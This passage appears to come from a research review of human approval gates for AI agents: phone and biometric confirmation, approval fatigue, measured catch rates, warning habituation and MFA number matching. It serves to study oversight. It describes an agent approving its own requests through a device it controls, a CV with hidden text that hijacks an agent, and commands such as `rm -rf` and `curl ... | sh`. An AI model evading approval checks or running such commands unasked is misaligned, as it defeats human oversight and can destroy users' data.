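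Expiry also limits how long one biometric check counts. A fingerprint check at 2:00 is poor evidence of who is holding the phone at 2:30, and even poorer evidence 18 hours later. Anthropic's Trusted Devices setting allows 18 hours between checks. Tsipursky argues that a narrow permission with a five-minute limit is easier to audit than one that stays active all afternoon.

Tsipursky says the record should also identify the agent, the limits of its authority, the person who decided, the version of the transaction they saw and the decision itself. Gervais adds that it should distinguish a fresh human approval from an action taken under an earlier permission. If the developer ticked "allow similar" in March and the agent used that permission in June, it would be misleading to record the June action as "approved by the developer".

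Confirming who someone is also doesn't establish what they're authorized to approve. *Provable Authority* (Blackburn, Hines and colleagues, 2026) describes a finance director whose delegated powers have changed since she received them. Her fingerprint would still match, and her signature would still be valid. In the paper's design, from the identity company ChainIT, software checks the approver's current authority just before a payment. It binds the result of that check and the biometric approval to a digest of the transaction. Once the payment is complete, the company seals the record. Any later refund or dispute goes into a new, linked record, so the original doesn't have to change.

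### When the approver wants the agent to decide

The previous cases assume that the approver wants to keep control. Breckenridge and colleagues separate "strong" protection from "weak" because an employee might prefer to let the agent approve its own requests.

If the signing key can't be exported from the hardware, a user can't copy it to the agent, but he could still register a second device that the agent controls. A World ID account, for example, can have several authenticators, and by default proofs from all of them look the same to the service. The service can block a device controlled by the agent by requiring evidence that each key is in genuine hardware and a genuine app.

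Even strong protection doesn't stop an approver from letting a colleague use his phone and PIN, because a human is still approving. Breckenridge and colleagues note that only a biometric check at every approval would prevent this, and they leave the problem outside their model. One of the devices they rate as strong, the Wultra Talisman, has no biometric sensor. Its user enters a PIN on a physical keypad that the agent can't press, but this doesn't stop another person who has the device and knows the PIN.

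The strong rating and the biometric check therefore provide different assurances. A company that wants to stop an agent from approving its own actions needs a protected key, a display that shows the action accurately, and a physical input. A PIN can be enough in place of a biometric. If the company must also show that a particular manager approved, it needs the biometric.

With strong protection, the employee also can't credibly claim that the agent approved a disastrous payment. This is fair if he read an accurate card and approved it anyway, but less fair if the record proves that he pressed the sensor but not what he saw. Breckenridge and colleagues suggest that strong approval records could help companies show compliance with laws that require human oversight, such as the EU's AI Act, but are "not evidence of due attention".

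### Shared phones and pressure from others

More than one person may be able to pass a phone's biometric check. Couples enrol each other's fingerprints, and a team may share one phone among whoever is on call. The secure hardware accepts any enrolled finger, and the signature doesn't reveal whose it was. If a key requires a biometric check for every use, Android disables it by default when someone adds a new fingerprint. On an iPhone, the app's developer chooses whether the key still works after such a change. Disabling the key stops people who enrol later from using it, but anyone who enrolled before the app created it can still use it.

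A team that shares a phone should give each member a separate passkey on their own device, or use a remote face check that identifies the individual. iProov markets its face check for shared devices, which are one of the few cases where checking on a server has a clear advantage over checking on the phone.

Neither method detects pressure. A person who approves a payment because a fraudster is on the phone still has the right face, is alive and is acting deliberately. The Paypers' *Veriff launches Presence Verification tool* reports UK losses of about £576 million in 2025 to authorised push payment fraud, in which victims are tricked into making the transfers themselves. To detect coercion, Veriff's product analyses the video and audio of the whole session for signs of coaching. The company reports accuracy above 98%.

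That figure is less impressive if coercion is rare. Suppose one approval in 10,000 is coerced, and the detector catches 98% of coerced approvals but also flags 2% of normal ones. In 10,000 approvals, it would probably catch the coerced one but also raise about 200 false alarms. The detector could be reasonable for a large transfer, where a bank can phone the customer back, but it would quickly become a nuisance for a developer approving actions every day.

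### Accessibility and privacy

Some people have worn or missing fingerprints, and others can't hold a phone steady for a selfie or see where the camera is pointing. iProov, which supplies a face check, claims in its listing on a UK government marketplace that it meets recognised accessibility standards and has tested the check with screen-reading tools on iPhones, on Android phones and in browsers. These claims don't show how many disabled users complete the check.

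For many people who can't use the sensor, a PIN on a trusted device is a good alternative. As the Talisman shows, a PIN can still keep the approval out of the agent's reach, though the company loses some assurance about which person approved. For sensitive actions, the company could make up for this by requiring a second approver, as long as the extra step doesn't make the job impractical for the person using the PIN.

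Checking on the phone is also better for privacy. The service receives a signature and a flag, and the fingerprint or face template stays on the device. In a remote check, images of the person's face go to the provider. iProov's contract terms have the client enrol each user under a pseudonym, so the provider doesn't need a name. But a face can identify someone without a name, and a person can't change their face after a leak as they could a password. Coercion detection requires even more data, and a recording of the whole session may capture other people in the room.

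Approval records can be sensitive even without biometric data, because they show whom someone pays and which files they send. Gervais and Tsipursky advise companies to keep the result of the check, not the images. For a developer who approves her own agent's pushes on her own phone, a fingerprint matched on that phone is usually enough. Sending a face scan to a server would reduce her privacy and add little proof.

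## How carefully do people read approval prompts?

A valid signature authorized by the right person's fingerprint doesn't show that she read the request first. To judge whether a phone makes people more careful, it helps to know how carefully they already read prompts on their own computers.

Most production agents rely on approval prompts. Wang, Li and Tian (2026) reviewed 21 systems in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* and found that none used "intent anchoring", in which another model judges whether each action fits the user's request. They argue that people have to stay involved because a request such as "fix this bug" leaves out much of what the user wants, and only the user can supply the rest.

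They also think current prompts work badly. They say that one task, such as "refactor the authentication module", can trigger dozens of prompts, and that users turn into "OK-button machines". This describes approval fatigue, in which people approve less carefully as the number of requests grows. The claim is plausible, but theirs is a position paper, and they support it mainly by analogy with browser warnings.

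### Approval rate and catch rate

Anthropic reported an approval rate of 93% for Claude Code and later one of 97%. It doesn't state the sample or the period for either rate, so the difference may not be a trend. Neither rate shows how carefully people read the prompts.

Suppose an agent makes 1,000 requests, of which 10 are harmful. One approver refuses all 10, along with 5 harmless ones. Another refuses 15 harmless requests and approves every harmful one. Both approve 985 requests, or 98.5%, but their catch rates are 100% and 0%.

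In general, if π is the share of requests that are harmful, c is the catch rate and f is the false refusal rate, then

`share refused = π × c + (1 − π) × f`

Claude Code's users refuse 3% of prompts, but Anthropic doesn't report what share of requests are harmful. If 1% are harmful, users could be refusing all, some or none of them, because the other refusals could be of harmless requests. If 10% were harmful, users could be refusing at most 30% of them.

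Anthropic also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so people evidently do say no in the same product. But a plan gives them more to disagree with than a single action does, and many rejections may concern taste or priorities. A developer who wants a different design will reject a safe plan, though she has little reason to reject a safe test run.

### Turning the prompts off

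Many people who tire of approval prompts turn them off. In February 2026, Anthropic published a study of how Claude Code users' habits change with experience. The Decoder reported that new users let the agent run without any manual approval in about 20% of sessions, and that the share passed 40% by roughly the 750th session.

The data cover all interactive use by people who signed up after 19 September 2025, according to The Greek Courier's *measuring ai agent autonomy in practice* (2026), which reprints Anthropic's text. According to the same text, growing trust may not be the only cause of the rise, because Claude Code asked for manual approval by default and some people may have taken time to find the setting they had wanted from the start.

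Users who stop approving each step may still supervise the agent. Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code* emphasises that experienced users also interrupt the agent more often, although The Decoder calls the difference small. Interrupting is useful when the agent drifts off course over several minutes, but less so against a single command that deletes a branch, because the branch may be gone before anyone reacts.

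Users can also keep the prompts but exempt whole classes of command. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the terminal version had written at least one rule approving shell commands in advance, and Anthropic said this share was growing by about 5 percentage points every five weeks. Many of these rules are broad. A rule that allows any Python program, for example, allows almost anything, since a Python program can delete files or contact a server. A quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that bypasses all permission checks.

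Because of these settings, the 97% approval rate covers only people who still get prompts and commands they haven't exempted. A developer who has exempted all her test commands no longer approves them one by one, and someone who bypasses every check isn't counted.

### What happens when a request is harmful

To measure a catch rate, researchers have to know which requests are harmful, so they usually plant harmful ones. The table compares three studies that did this in 2026. For the two smaller studies, it includes only the groups that approved actions individually from an ordinary description.

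| Study | Approvers | Harmful requests per person | Catch rate | False refusal rate | Time per request |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | 1,053 paid testers | 1 in a whole session | 13.6% | Not reported | Not reported |
| Hossain and colleagues | 20 volunteers | 6 of 12 | 45.0% | 8.3% | 16.3 s (median) |
| Yan | 34 people outside the software industry | 7 of 18 | 59.6% | 5.9% | 7.9 s (average) |

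Anthropic's testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. The dangerous command replaced an ordinary permission prompt partway through the session. The sample is large enough that chance would move the result by only about two percentage points either way.

The catch rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The drop is consistent with approval fatigue but isn't clean evidence of it. Each tester saw only one dangerous command, so the comparison is between different people. People who click through prompts quickly reach the fiftieth sooner than people who read them, so the late group may have contained more fast clickers from the start. Anthropic doesn't say whether it chose the dangerous prompt's position at random.

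The published figures also omit how often the testers refused harmless commands. If they refused 13% of those too, they weren't distinguishing dangerous commands from safe ones. That seems unlikely, because Claude Code's users rarely refuse anything, but the figures don't rule it out. Anthropic also published the study to support its switch to automated review, and a low human score strengthens its case.

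In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), participants supervised a simulated assistant through a day of email, an airport trip and some tidying up afterwards. The day's goals required 11 of the 18 actions, and the other 7 went beyond what the user had asked for. Every prompt described the action in plain language, including any amount, recipient or data involved.

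People's decisions depended heavily on the action. Of the 34 who were asked to approve each action individually, 27 refused to let the assistant post publicly that the user was travelling, 22 refused to let it read recent bank transactions, and only 4 refused to let it call the airport to confirm a flight. Yan counted the call as overreach because nobody had asked for it, but participants may have read the prompt carefully and thought the call was a good idea. Excluding the call, the catch rate would have been about 68%. A catch rate therefore depends partly on who decides what counts as harmful, especially when the harm is overreach.

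Yan's study also found no sign that people who saw fewer prompts reviewed them more carefully. A second group saw about 10 prompts instead of 18 because a model handled the other actions. They approved 46% of the overreach actions, against 40% in the group that saw everything. A third group, which wrote standing rules first, saw about 11 prompts on average and approved 67% of the overreach actions that reached them. This last comparison is less reliable because each person's rules determined which prompts appeared and Yan recruited some of that group separately. Reducing the number of prompts may not have helped because even a day of 18 prompts was too short to tire anyone.

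Hossain and colleagues also tested comprehension, and people who saw only a short description answered 57.1% of the questions correctly. They made some of their errors because they lacked the facts, not because they failed to read them, so the 45% catch rate shouldn't be blamed entirely on the approvers.

The gap between 13.6% and 59.6% has several possible explanations. Yan's and Hossain's participants only had to judge requests, and one in every two or three was harmful. Yan's participants had also just answered questions about which actions an assistant should take on its own, which probably made them think about permissions. Anthropic's testers were trying to finish a coding task and had seen only harmless prompts. Their situation is closer to a developer's working day, though they had no code of their own to protect. Hossain and colleagues expect habituation to become the main risk when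 harmful requests are rare, and recommend that future studies vary the proportion of harmful requests.

Evidence from real work is harder to interpret. Anthropic examined sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. In 6.3% of those that used manual approval, the agent took a harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, comparable in severity to deleting rows from a production database. Somebody may have approved these actions, or an earlier rule may have allowed them. A language model graded the sessions. Because the sample contained only flagged sessions, 6.3% isn't the rate of harm in ordinary use.

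### Confidence is a poor guide

Approvers can't easily tell from how they feel whether they are paying enough attention. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) gave 36 people six programming tasks each to complete with a coding agent. In some tasks, the agent wrote code that passed the automatic checks but broke a less obvious requirement. Participants found and fixed these defects in 28 of 71 cases. They rated their confidence in the solution at 4 or 5 out of 5 in 79% of the cases they missed.

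The 39% success rate doesn't belong in the table above because participants were checking finished code for defects, not reviewing approval prompts. Their overconfidence probably applies to approval prompts too, because a misleading request also looks complete and plausible. Participants were better at judging their effort. On average, they rated their checking as more thorough on tasks where they caught the defect. They also spent longer on those tasks, 10.8 minutes compared with 5.8 when they missed it, though some of that time must have gone into the repair.

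People checked more carefully after a visible failure, but apparently not for long. When the defective code came directly after a task in which the checks had failed, participants fixed 12 of 24 defects. When a correct task came in between, they fixed 1 of 11. The second sample is small and different tasks appeared in different positions, but the difference remained after a statistical adjustment for task difficulty. In earlier interviews by the same researchers, one person said that discovering an AI had cited a nonexistent article "snapped me out of it".

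Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, tested whether people notice when an attacker has compromised their AI agent. The 303 participants used a compromised agent for realistic tasks, such as picking the best candidate from a set of CVs, one of which contained hidden text that changed the agent's ranking. With only a disclaimer at the start, 8.6% later reported something unusual. The share was 20.0% with a reminder beside every answer and 25.0% with an alert that interrupted the work when the agent's output was suspicious. Before the tasks, three quarters of the participants said they often check an AI's output.

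Nobody had to approve or refuse a particular action, so this isn't a catch rate. The exact percentages also call for some caution because the paper gives two incompatible sets of group sizes, roughly 100 people per group in one place and 183, 60 and 60 in another. Even so, three quarters of people apparently didn't register an interrupting alert as a sign of trouble, which is discouraging for anyone relying on prompts.

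Li and colleagues' numbers barely support their conclusion that technical experts are more vulnerable than others because they trust the agent's process while concentrating on its output. In the disclaimer group, 6.8% of the experts and 9.6% of the others noticed something, a difference of two or three people. Dissanayake and colleagues found the opposite in their programming study, where beginners fixed 17% of the hidden defects, intermediate programmers 39% and advanced programmers 57%. Knowing the subject seems to help when the problem lies in the code itself, but it is less clear whether it helps someone recognise a manipulated agent. Experience with AI agents, unlike programming skill, made no measurable difference in the programming study.

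*From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), a study of developers' habits with coding agents, suggests that those who watch the agent's output and interrupt when necessary review individual approval requests less closely. That could be sensible, since a developer who has followed the agent for ten minutes already knows why it wants to run the tests. But the habit fails when she looks away and returns to a prompt without having seen what led to it. There may also be little to check afterwards, because only 20% of the developers logged or audited their agents' actions.

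### Habituation

Researchers studied why people ignore security warnings long before coding agents existed. A large part of the explanation is habituation, which means that people pay less attention to something as they see it repeatedly. A developer who intends to read every prompt can still stop noticing them, which is different from deciding that test commands aren't worth the effort of reading.

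*How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain* (Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues, 2015) used brain imaging to measure habituation to security warnings. People viewed warnings repeatedly while a scanner recorded activity in the brain's visual areas. Activity fell sharply the second time they saw a warning and kept falling with later viewings. This shows reduced visual processing, which isn't the same as a bad decision, but someone who barely processes a warning is poorly placed to act on it.

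Vance, Jenkins and colleagues (2018), in *Tuning Out Security Warnings*, followed the effect over longer periods. In one experiment, they combined brain imaging with eye tracking over a five-day working week. Attention to the warnings declined with repetition and recovered only partly overnight. In a second experiment, people installed apps on their own phones for three weeks and heeded fewer of the permission warnings as time went on. In both experiments, the decline was smaller when the warning's appearance kept changing.

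Habituation can also spread from one message to another. *The Fog of Warnings*, by Vance, Eargle and colleagues (2019), reports that people who had become used to routine notifications also paid less attention to security warnings that resembled them. *Trained to Accept?*, by Böhme and Köpsell (2010), reports a similar effect from a field experiment that varied a consent dialog for about 80,000 users of an online privacy tool. Users were more likely to accept when the dialog looked more like a software licence agreement. They seemed to respond to the type of dialog before considering what they were agreeing to.

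Terminal prompts show routine and dangerous commands in the same box, so each routine approval makes people more likely to approve a dangerous command out of habit.

Bravo-Lillo, Komanduri and colleagues (2013) tested a very similar situation in *Your Attention, Please*. Participants repeatedly dismissed a dialog in which one field contained nothing useful, and then the researchers put critical information in that field. Participants who saw the ordinary dialog often missed the information, and did much worse than those whose dialog delayed them until they had dealt with the field. An approval card changes in the same way when its layout has been constant for weeks and a second recipient appears on one line.

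Even people who care about the consequences can become habituated to prompts, and habituation may even be efficient. If a developer gets 100 prompts a day and spends 16 seconds on each, as Hossain's participants did with the short description, she spends about 27 minutes a day reading them. If one request in 1,000 is harmful, she reads for about four and a half hours for each harmful request she sees, and at a 45% catch rate she would more likely than not approve it. For commands that she can easily undo, reading less is a reasonable response to those odds. But she can't reserve her attention for the exceptions unless something about the prompt distinguishes them.

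### Warnings that people heed

Some research on warnings is more encouraging. In *Alice in Warningland*, Akhawe and Felt (2013) analyzed data on more than 25 million warnings that Chrome and Firefox showed people during ordinary browsing. Users clicked through about a tenth of Firefox's malware and phishing warnings and about a quarter of Chrome's.

Results were worse for SSL warnings, which appear when the browser can't verify a website's identity. Firefox users clicked through a third of them and Chrome users 70%. Wang and colleagues, who argue against current approval prompts, put the figure above 90%. The browser data don't support a number that high, let alone the claim that people ignore every warning.

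The difference between the browsers suggests that design matters, but design can't explain all of it, because Firefox and Chrome had different users and handled repeat visits to a problem site differently. Like an approval rate, a click-through rate also doesn't separate good decisions from bad ones. Many SSL warnings came from harmless mistakes in a site's setup, and a user who clicked through to her employer's misconfigured page had made the right choice.

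That may be part of the reason people took malware warnings more seriously. The warnings were uncommon and usually meant that something was wrong. Approval prompts for agents, by contrast, appear many times a day, and nearly all of them are for actions the user wants.

Yan's participants nevertheless refused most of the requests to read private messages or permanently delete an old file. Anybody could recognise the consequences of those requests, and the participants had nothing else to do. A developer asked to approve `rm -rf` followed by a long path at the end of an afternoon has other work to do, and the consequences are harder to recognise.

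## Does a second device or a biometric step make people evaluate better?

No published experiment appears to have compared how well people judge the same agent request in a terminal and on a phone. Kodathala and colleagues say it would take a user study to learn whether a separate device changes what people notice, and they haven't run one. They found that the phone added nothing over a prompt on the same computer, but their approvers were simulated. Hossain's and Yan's experiments involved people, but they varied what the prompt displayed or who wrote the rules, not the device.

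The remaining evidence is indirect. Moving an approval to a phone changes several things at once, and each could help or hurt evaluation. Researchers have tested some of these changes in banking, logins, security warnings and AI advice.

| What changes | How it could help | How it could hurt |
|---|---|---|
| The device | Interrupts the habit of pressing the same key | Becomes a habit of its own |
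| The time it takes | Gives the approver a moment to notice a problem | Irritates people, who then turn approvals off |
| The screen | Shows one card with few distractions | Hides long commands and code changes |
| The setting | Lets the approver look at the request afresh | Separates her from the files and history she needs |
| The gesture | Makes approval feel like a decision | Can become as automatic as a key press |
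| The biometric check | Resembles approving a payment | Can take less effort than typing |

In the best case for the phone, a developer has approved 40 harmless commands in the terminal since lunch when a request to delete several shared branches goes to her phone. She has to stop typing, pick up the phone and read a card that looks nothing like the terminal prompt. Before she touches the sensor, she notices that one of the branches belongs to a colleague who is still using it. If few requests reach her phone, she can tell from the notification alone that this one is unusual.

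The best argument that phone approval makes people evaluate worse is that the same request could arrive while she is in a queue at the supermarket. She remembers asking the agent to tidy up the branches, but not which ones are still in use. At her desk she would have looked them up before answering, but here she can't easily check. The agent can't continue until she answers, and she has already unlocked her phone with her thumb dozens of times that day, so she presses her thumb again and approves the request.

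### Checking a bank transfer on a phone

The closest evidence on how people read a second screen comes from online banking. Banks texted a transfer's details to the customer's phone, and the customer was supposed to notice if malware on the computer had changed the destination account.

AlZomai, Alfayyadh and colleagues examined this kind of protection in *An Experimental Investigation of the Usability of Transaction Authorization* (2008). According to Finextra's *SMS banking passwords fail to stop hackers*, they simulated an online bank and altered account numbers, changing five or more digits in "obvious" attacks and only one in "stealthy" attacks.

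People missed the obvious attacks, which made large changes, 21% of the time and the stealthy ones, which made small changes, 61% of the time. *Display Security for Online Transactions* (Alzomai, Alfayyadh and Jøsang, 2010) gives the same percentages but describes the obvious attack as a change to half the digits. It doesn't give the number of participants, so it is hard to know how precise the percentages are. The figures are for checking details on a phone, so they don't show whether people would have done better or worse on a computer.

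The result applies fairly well to payments and emails that an agent proposes, where the approver also has to spot a wrong account or address. If anything, the agent's user has a harder task. The bank customer had just typed the correct account number and could compare the two screens, but when an agent finds an invoice and proposes to pay it, the user may never have seen the correct number.

The bank study applies less well to shell commands, because a developer usually has no correct version of the command to compare with the one on the card. She has to work out what the command would do and whether she wants that. She could read every character of `python3 deploy.py` accurately and still approve something harmful. But the study does apply to the long identifiers inside technical requests. A full commit identifier usually has 40 characters, and a person who misses one changed digit among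 eight is unlikely to check all 40.

The banking figures also raise doubts about the simulations of agent approval. One of Kodathala's simulated approvers, designed to overlook some details, missed a change to the first part of an email address 20% of the time and a plainly different host 5% of the time. The researchers state that they assumed these rates. Bank customers missed large changes at close to the 20% rate, but they missed a change to a single digit three times as often. The simulations may therefore overstate how well people catch small changes.

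Alzomai and colleagues concluded that software should do the comparison. In their design, the customer photographs the computer's display with a phone. The phone converts the picture to text and compares it with the bank's message. In 60 attempts by 12 people, the conversion produced valid text 49 times (82%).

The gateway already holds the exact arguments of an agent's request, so no photograph is needed. ASU already checks whether a recipient is new, and a warning that says "You have never paid this account" takes the approver much less effort to evaluate than a row of digits.

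### Comparing codes on two screens

Jubur, Saxena and Reegu (2025), in *Usability and Security Analysis of the Compare-and-Confirm Method*, tested whether people can compare a short code on two screens. The login system they tested shows one code on the login page and another in the phone notification, and the user should approve only if the codes match.

Each of the 65 participants made 24 logins, half of them simulated attacks with codes that didn't match. In one example, the login page showed `L1BO` and the phone showed `JX0E`. The researchers had explained the method, let participants practise and told them they could deny anything suspicious. Participants still approved about 49.5% of the attacks.

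For half of the logins, participants used a desktop computer and confirmed on a phone. For the other half, they did everything on the phone, switching between the browser and the authentication app. The researchers expected more mistakes on the single device because people couldn't see both codes at once. They found no significant difference in how many attacks or genuine logins people approved. People approved 98.48% of genuine logins with two devices and 95.76% with one.

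This study comes closest to testing device switching, and it doesn't support the idea that a separate phone makes people more attentive. With up to 390 attack logins in each setting, a large difference is unlikely, but one of a few percentage points can't be ruled out. Participants answered on the phone in both settings, so the study doesn't show what would have happened if they had answered on the computer.

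The task differs from agent approval in other ways. Participants logged in to a made-up account in a laboratory and had nothing to lose. The codes were also just four random characters, and a person may look more carefully at an unfamiliar recipient. On the other hand, checking two short codes is much easier than judging a command, and half of the logins were attacks, far more than an approver would face at work.

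People may also find a comparison easy without doing it well. Jubur and colleagues summarise an older study by Uzun and co-authors in which people paired two devices by comparing two-digit numbers or by selecting the matching number from a group. Participants found both methods easy but considered them less secure. A favourable usability survey of agent approvals would similarly be weak evidence of the catch rate.

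### Login requests and number matching

Login notifications provide evidence from ordinary use. Weinert (2022), in *Defend your users from MFA fatigue attacks*, a post on a Microsoft blog, reported that about 1% of users accept a simple approval request on the first try. That sounds reassuring, but an attacker who has the password can keep asking. If each request had an independent 1% chance of success, 100 requests would give a chance of at least one approval of

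`1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 63%`

In practice, a person's decisions about successive requests are not independent. They may recognise the first request as an attack and refuse all the others, or they may get tired and give in at the end. CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, warns in *Implementing Number Matching in MFA Applications* that attackers can send hundreds of prompts in a short time and that some users accept one by accident.

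The 1% figure is far below the 49.5% in Jubur's laboratory, probably in part because of when the requests arrived. An attacker's login request often arrives when the user isn't logging in to anything, so the notification itself is a sign of trouble. In the laboratory, every attack arrived just when the participant was expecting a request. Agent approvals are similar, because a developer who has set an agent to work expects requests from it, and a harmful one doesn't stand out by its timing.

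Attackers can use the same expectation against real logins. *Countering Concurrent Login Attacks in "Just Tap" Push-based Authentication* (Prakash, Chua and colleagues, 2023) describes an attacker who starts a login at the same moment as the user. Two requests reach the phone, and a plain "approve" button gives the user no way to tell them apart. A developer running several agents could face a similar problem if she approves a push for one agent, then sees a second card and assumes it belongs to the same job. An approval card that shows the stored action lets her tell the two requests apart, provided she reads it.

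Login services now commonly use number matching to stop accidental approvals. The login page displays a number, and the user has to enter it in the phone app. WA SOC's *Number Matching in Multifactor Authentication* (2023), a Western Australian government advisory, points out that attackers can no longer get in by sending many prompts, because the user can't accept one without knowing its number. The number is displayed on the attacker's screen, which the user doesn't see.

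Number matching therefore works by withholding a number the user needs, not by improving the user's judgement. It would do much less against a harmful request from the developer's own agent, because the number would appear on her screen beside the request and she would enter it correctly. This would show that she had noticed the request and connected it with the right session, but not that she had thought about the action. If the agent had taken control of the host, it could also display whatever number it needed. She also couldn't approve anything while away from her desk, and people often want phone approval so that they can do that.

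A designer could keep the typing but change what the approver types. To approve deleting a branch, for example, the approver might have to enter its name or the number of commits that would be lost. She would then have to look at the part of the card that matters, but she could still copy the name without considering whether anyone needs the branch.

### Delay and extra effort

*DuoLungo* (2026), a field study of 2,559 people at the University of California, Irvine, measured Duo login approvals over an academic year. A push approval added nearly 8 seconds on average, a delay participants described as short to moderate. People failed to complete 4.35% of the approvals, and 43.86% of survey respondents remembered at least one failed login.

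Eight seconds is enough to read a short card, but people may spend it finding the phone, unlocking it and waiting for the notification, then approve as quickly as before. The study measured how much time switching devices added, and its participants were approving their own logins, so it doesn't show whether they used that time to think.

Hossain and colleagues found that people decided faster with the consequence card than with the full log and did at least as well at refusing harmful requests, so slower decisions are not necessarily better. The short description led to the quickest decisions and the most approvals of harmful requests, but it also gave people the least to read. A delay adds no information if the screen still shows the same short description.

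Extra information also made the work harder. On a standard questionnaire that scores mental workload from 0 to 100, participants who saw the short description averaged 27.3, compared with 44.3 for the log and 43.0 for the consequence card. If careful approval is this much more demanding, an approver can't be expected to keep it up for every request, whichever device she uses.

Delays seem to help when people have to use them to look at something specific, such as the critical field in Bravo-Lillo's experiment. This supports a card that requires the approver to open the list of branches before the approve button works. It gives less support to using a phone just because it is slower, since the approver can look at anything during the delay. The critical information in that experiment was also plain text that anyone could understand, whereas making someone look at `curl ... | sh` doesn't teach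 them what it does.

Designers of AI assistants have tried cognitive forcing functions, which interrupt a quick, intuitive answer and make the person think, for example by asking for their own view before showing them the software's. Buçinca, Malaya and Gajos reported in 2021 that such features can reduce overreliance on AI advice.

*AI Watchdog* (2026) is a newer test with a less straightforward result. Participants talked with an AI that tried to steer their decisions, while separate software monitored the conversation. In two of the five groups, the software interrupted participants with a prompt to reconsider the exchange in their own terms. One of these groups could dismiss the prompt immediately, while the other had to write a response before continuing. Two more groups received training beforehand, one of them with a writing exercise, and a control group received nothing.

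Only the prompt that people could dismiss produced a statistically significant reduction in compliance with the AI's steering (p = 0.004 after correction for multiple comparisons). The prompt that required a written response did not. The difference between the two prompts could still be small, so this doesn't prove that requiring a response is worse, but it weakens the assumption that more effort always produces more thought. People who have to write something may concentrate on getting past the prompt.

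The participants were resisting persuasion in a conversation rather than judging a command. The software also monitored the conversation before interrupting, whereas an approval gate interrupts for every action of a certain type. The part most worth copying is probably the question written for the particular request. For the branch deletion, the card could ask "Is anyone still working on `payments-fix`?" The trusted software would have to write the question, because an agent trying to get the deletion approved would ask an easier one.

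### What the approver can't see from her phone

Approving on a phone may focus the approver's attention but hide information she needs to decide. *From Delegation to Action Approval* provides some evidence of what could be lost. It surveyed 202 developers on how often they approved seven types of agent action without close review. Those who inspected diffs, the line-by-line lists of changes to files, were less likely to approve four of the riskiest types this way: reading secrets, accessing private data, changing production settings and running destructive commands.

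The correlations were modest (between −0.25 and −0.33), and the study relied on developers' self-reports. Cautious people may inspect diffs and read approval requests without one habit causing the other. Still, the study's explanation that a diff gives the developer something concrete to check is plausible. Diffs are awkward to read on a phone, so moving approvals there could discourage developers from inspecting them, the one habit that the study linked to closer review.

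The same survey offers little evidence that developers who review code carefully also review the agent's actions carefully. Of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could easily be due to chance. Developers may read code line by line because they expect to find mistakes in it, yet treat an approval prompt as an interruption. They could easily treat a phone notification the same way.

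Moving approval to a second device also doesn't help when the request explains too little. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of trouble with agents and files, and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, users had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the prompt showed a command without explaining its effect on the user's files, as when `python3 setup.py` runs code hidden in a script. Some reports fell into both groups.

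Phone approval would not have helped users who saw only `python3 setup.py` unless the card had also included more explanation. It could have helped the larger group if the gateway had required a decision for the most dangerous actions. But many of those users had turned prompts off to avoid answering hundreds in a session, and having to pick up a phone for each one would have given them even more reason to turn them off.

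Where someone answers may matter more than the size of the screen. A developer who answers on a phone beside her laptop can still inspect the files and the agent's earlier steps. If she answers on a train, she may have only the approval card. Being away from her work could occasionally help, because someone absorbed in a task tends to approve whatever gets it finished, and she might judge a request more calmly at a distance. No study has measured this effect for agent approvals. The card could include an "ask me again at my desk" button so that she can postpone the decision instead of refusing or guessing.

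### What the fingerprint or face check adds

The biometric step has the least evidence behind it. *User-to-PC Authentication Through Confirmation on Mobile Devices* (Pramendorfer and Findling, 2025) compared tapping a button with using a fingerprint, on both a phone and a smartwatch. Thirty people each logged in to a computer or approved extra privileges on it 40 times. The study measured speed, success and usability, but not whether people could recognise a request they should refuse.

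Approving on the watch was faster than typing a password or using the phone, and participants rated the watch most usable. The phone came last, behind the password. Everyone used the password first, so practice may have affected that comparison, but the order of the other methods was random.

People's preference for approvals that take little effort is a problem for anyone who relies on friction. Companies have good commercial reasons to provide such approvals, but they can't consistently advertise an approval as effortless and also claim that the effort makes people careful. If the phone helps by making people stop, a faster sensor or an approval button on a watch would reduce that benefit. A watch would also have even less room for the card.

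How much effort a biometric check adds depends on what it replaces. It takes more effort than pressing a key in the terminal, but less than typing a password or the name of a branch. A face check can take almost no effort, unless designers start it only after the user has scrolled through the approval card and pressed approve. Any gain in attention would then come from the order of the steps, so a PIN or an ordinary button in the same place might work just as well.

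Weinert's description of login approvals supports the same conclusion. He counts "enter your PIN to approve" as a simple approval, like a click, because neither requires the user to know anything about the session. A fingerprint doesn't require this either. It is much stronger evidence than a tap of who approved the action, but it gives that person no information about the action to help them decide.

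A fingerprint might even make people less careful if they feel that the security check has already been done. This is speculation, but people's sense of control doesn't reliably reflect how well they are protected. In Yan's study, participants reported feeling highly in control under all three ways of handling permissions, with no reliable difference between them. Yet the group that wrote its own rules blocked about 20 percentage points less overreach than the group that approved actions one at a time.

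Many people confirm payments with a fingerprint, so being asked for one may remind them that something is at stake. But they also use it to unlock their phones, which happens far more often and has no such association. People get used to gestures as well as warnings, so touching the sensor could become as automatic as pressing the "yes" key in a terminal.

### An experiment that would settle the question

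In a good experiment, researchers would randomly assign developers to four groups, show everyone the same approval card generated by the gateway, and vary only how each group answers it.

| Group | Compare with | What a difference would show |
|---|---|---|
| Terminal | | |
| Terminal, approve button inactive for 8 seconds | Terminal | The effect of a delay |
| Phone, tap to approve | Terminal with delay | The combined effect of the device, screen and setting |
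| Phone, biometric check to approve | Phone with tap | The effect of the biometric check |

The delay comes from the Duo study, and a pilot should adjust it to match the time participants take to reach their phones. Without the delayed group, a higher catch rate on the phone could be due to the few extra seconds rather than the phone itself. The delayed prompt would also be much cheaper to deploy, so a company would want to know if it worked equally well, at least where the agent can't control the host.

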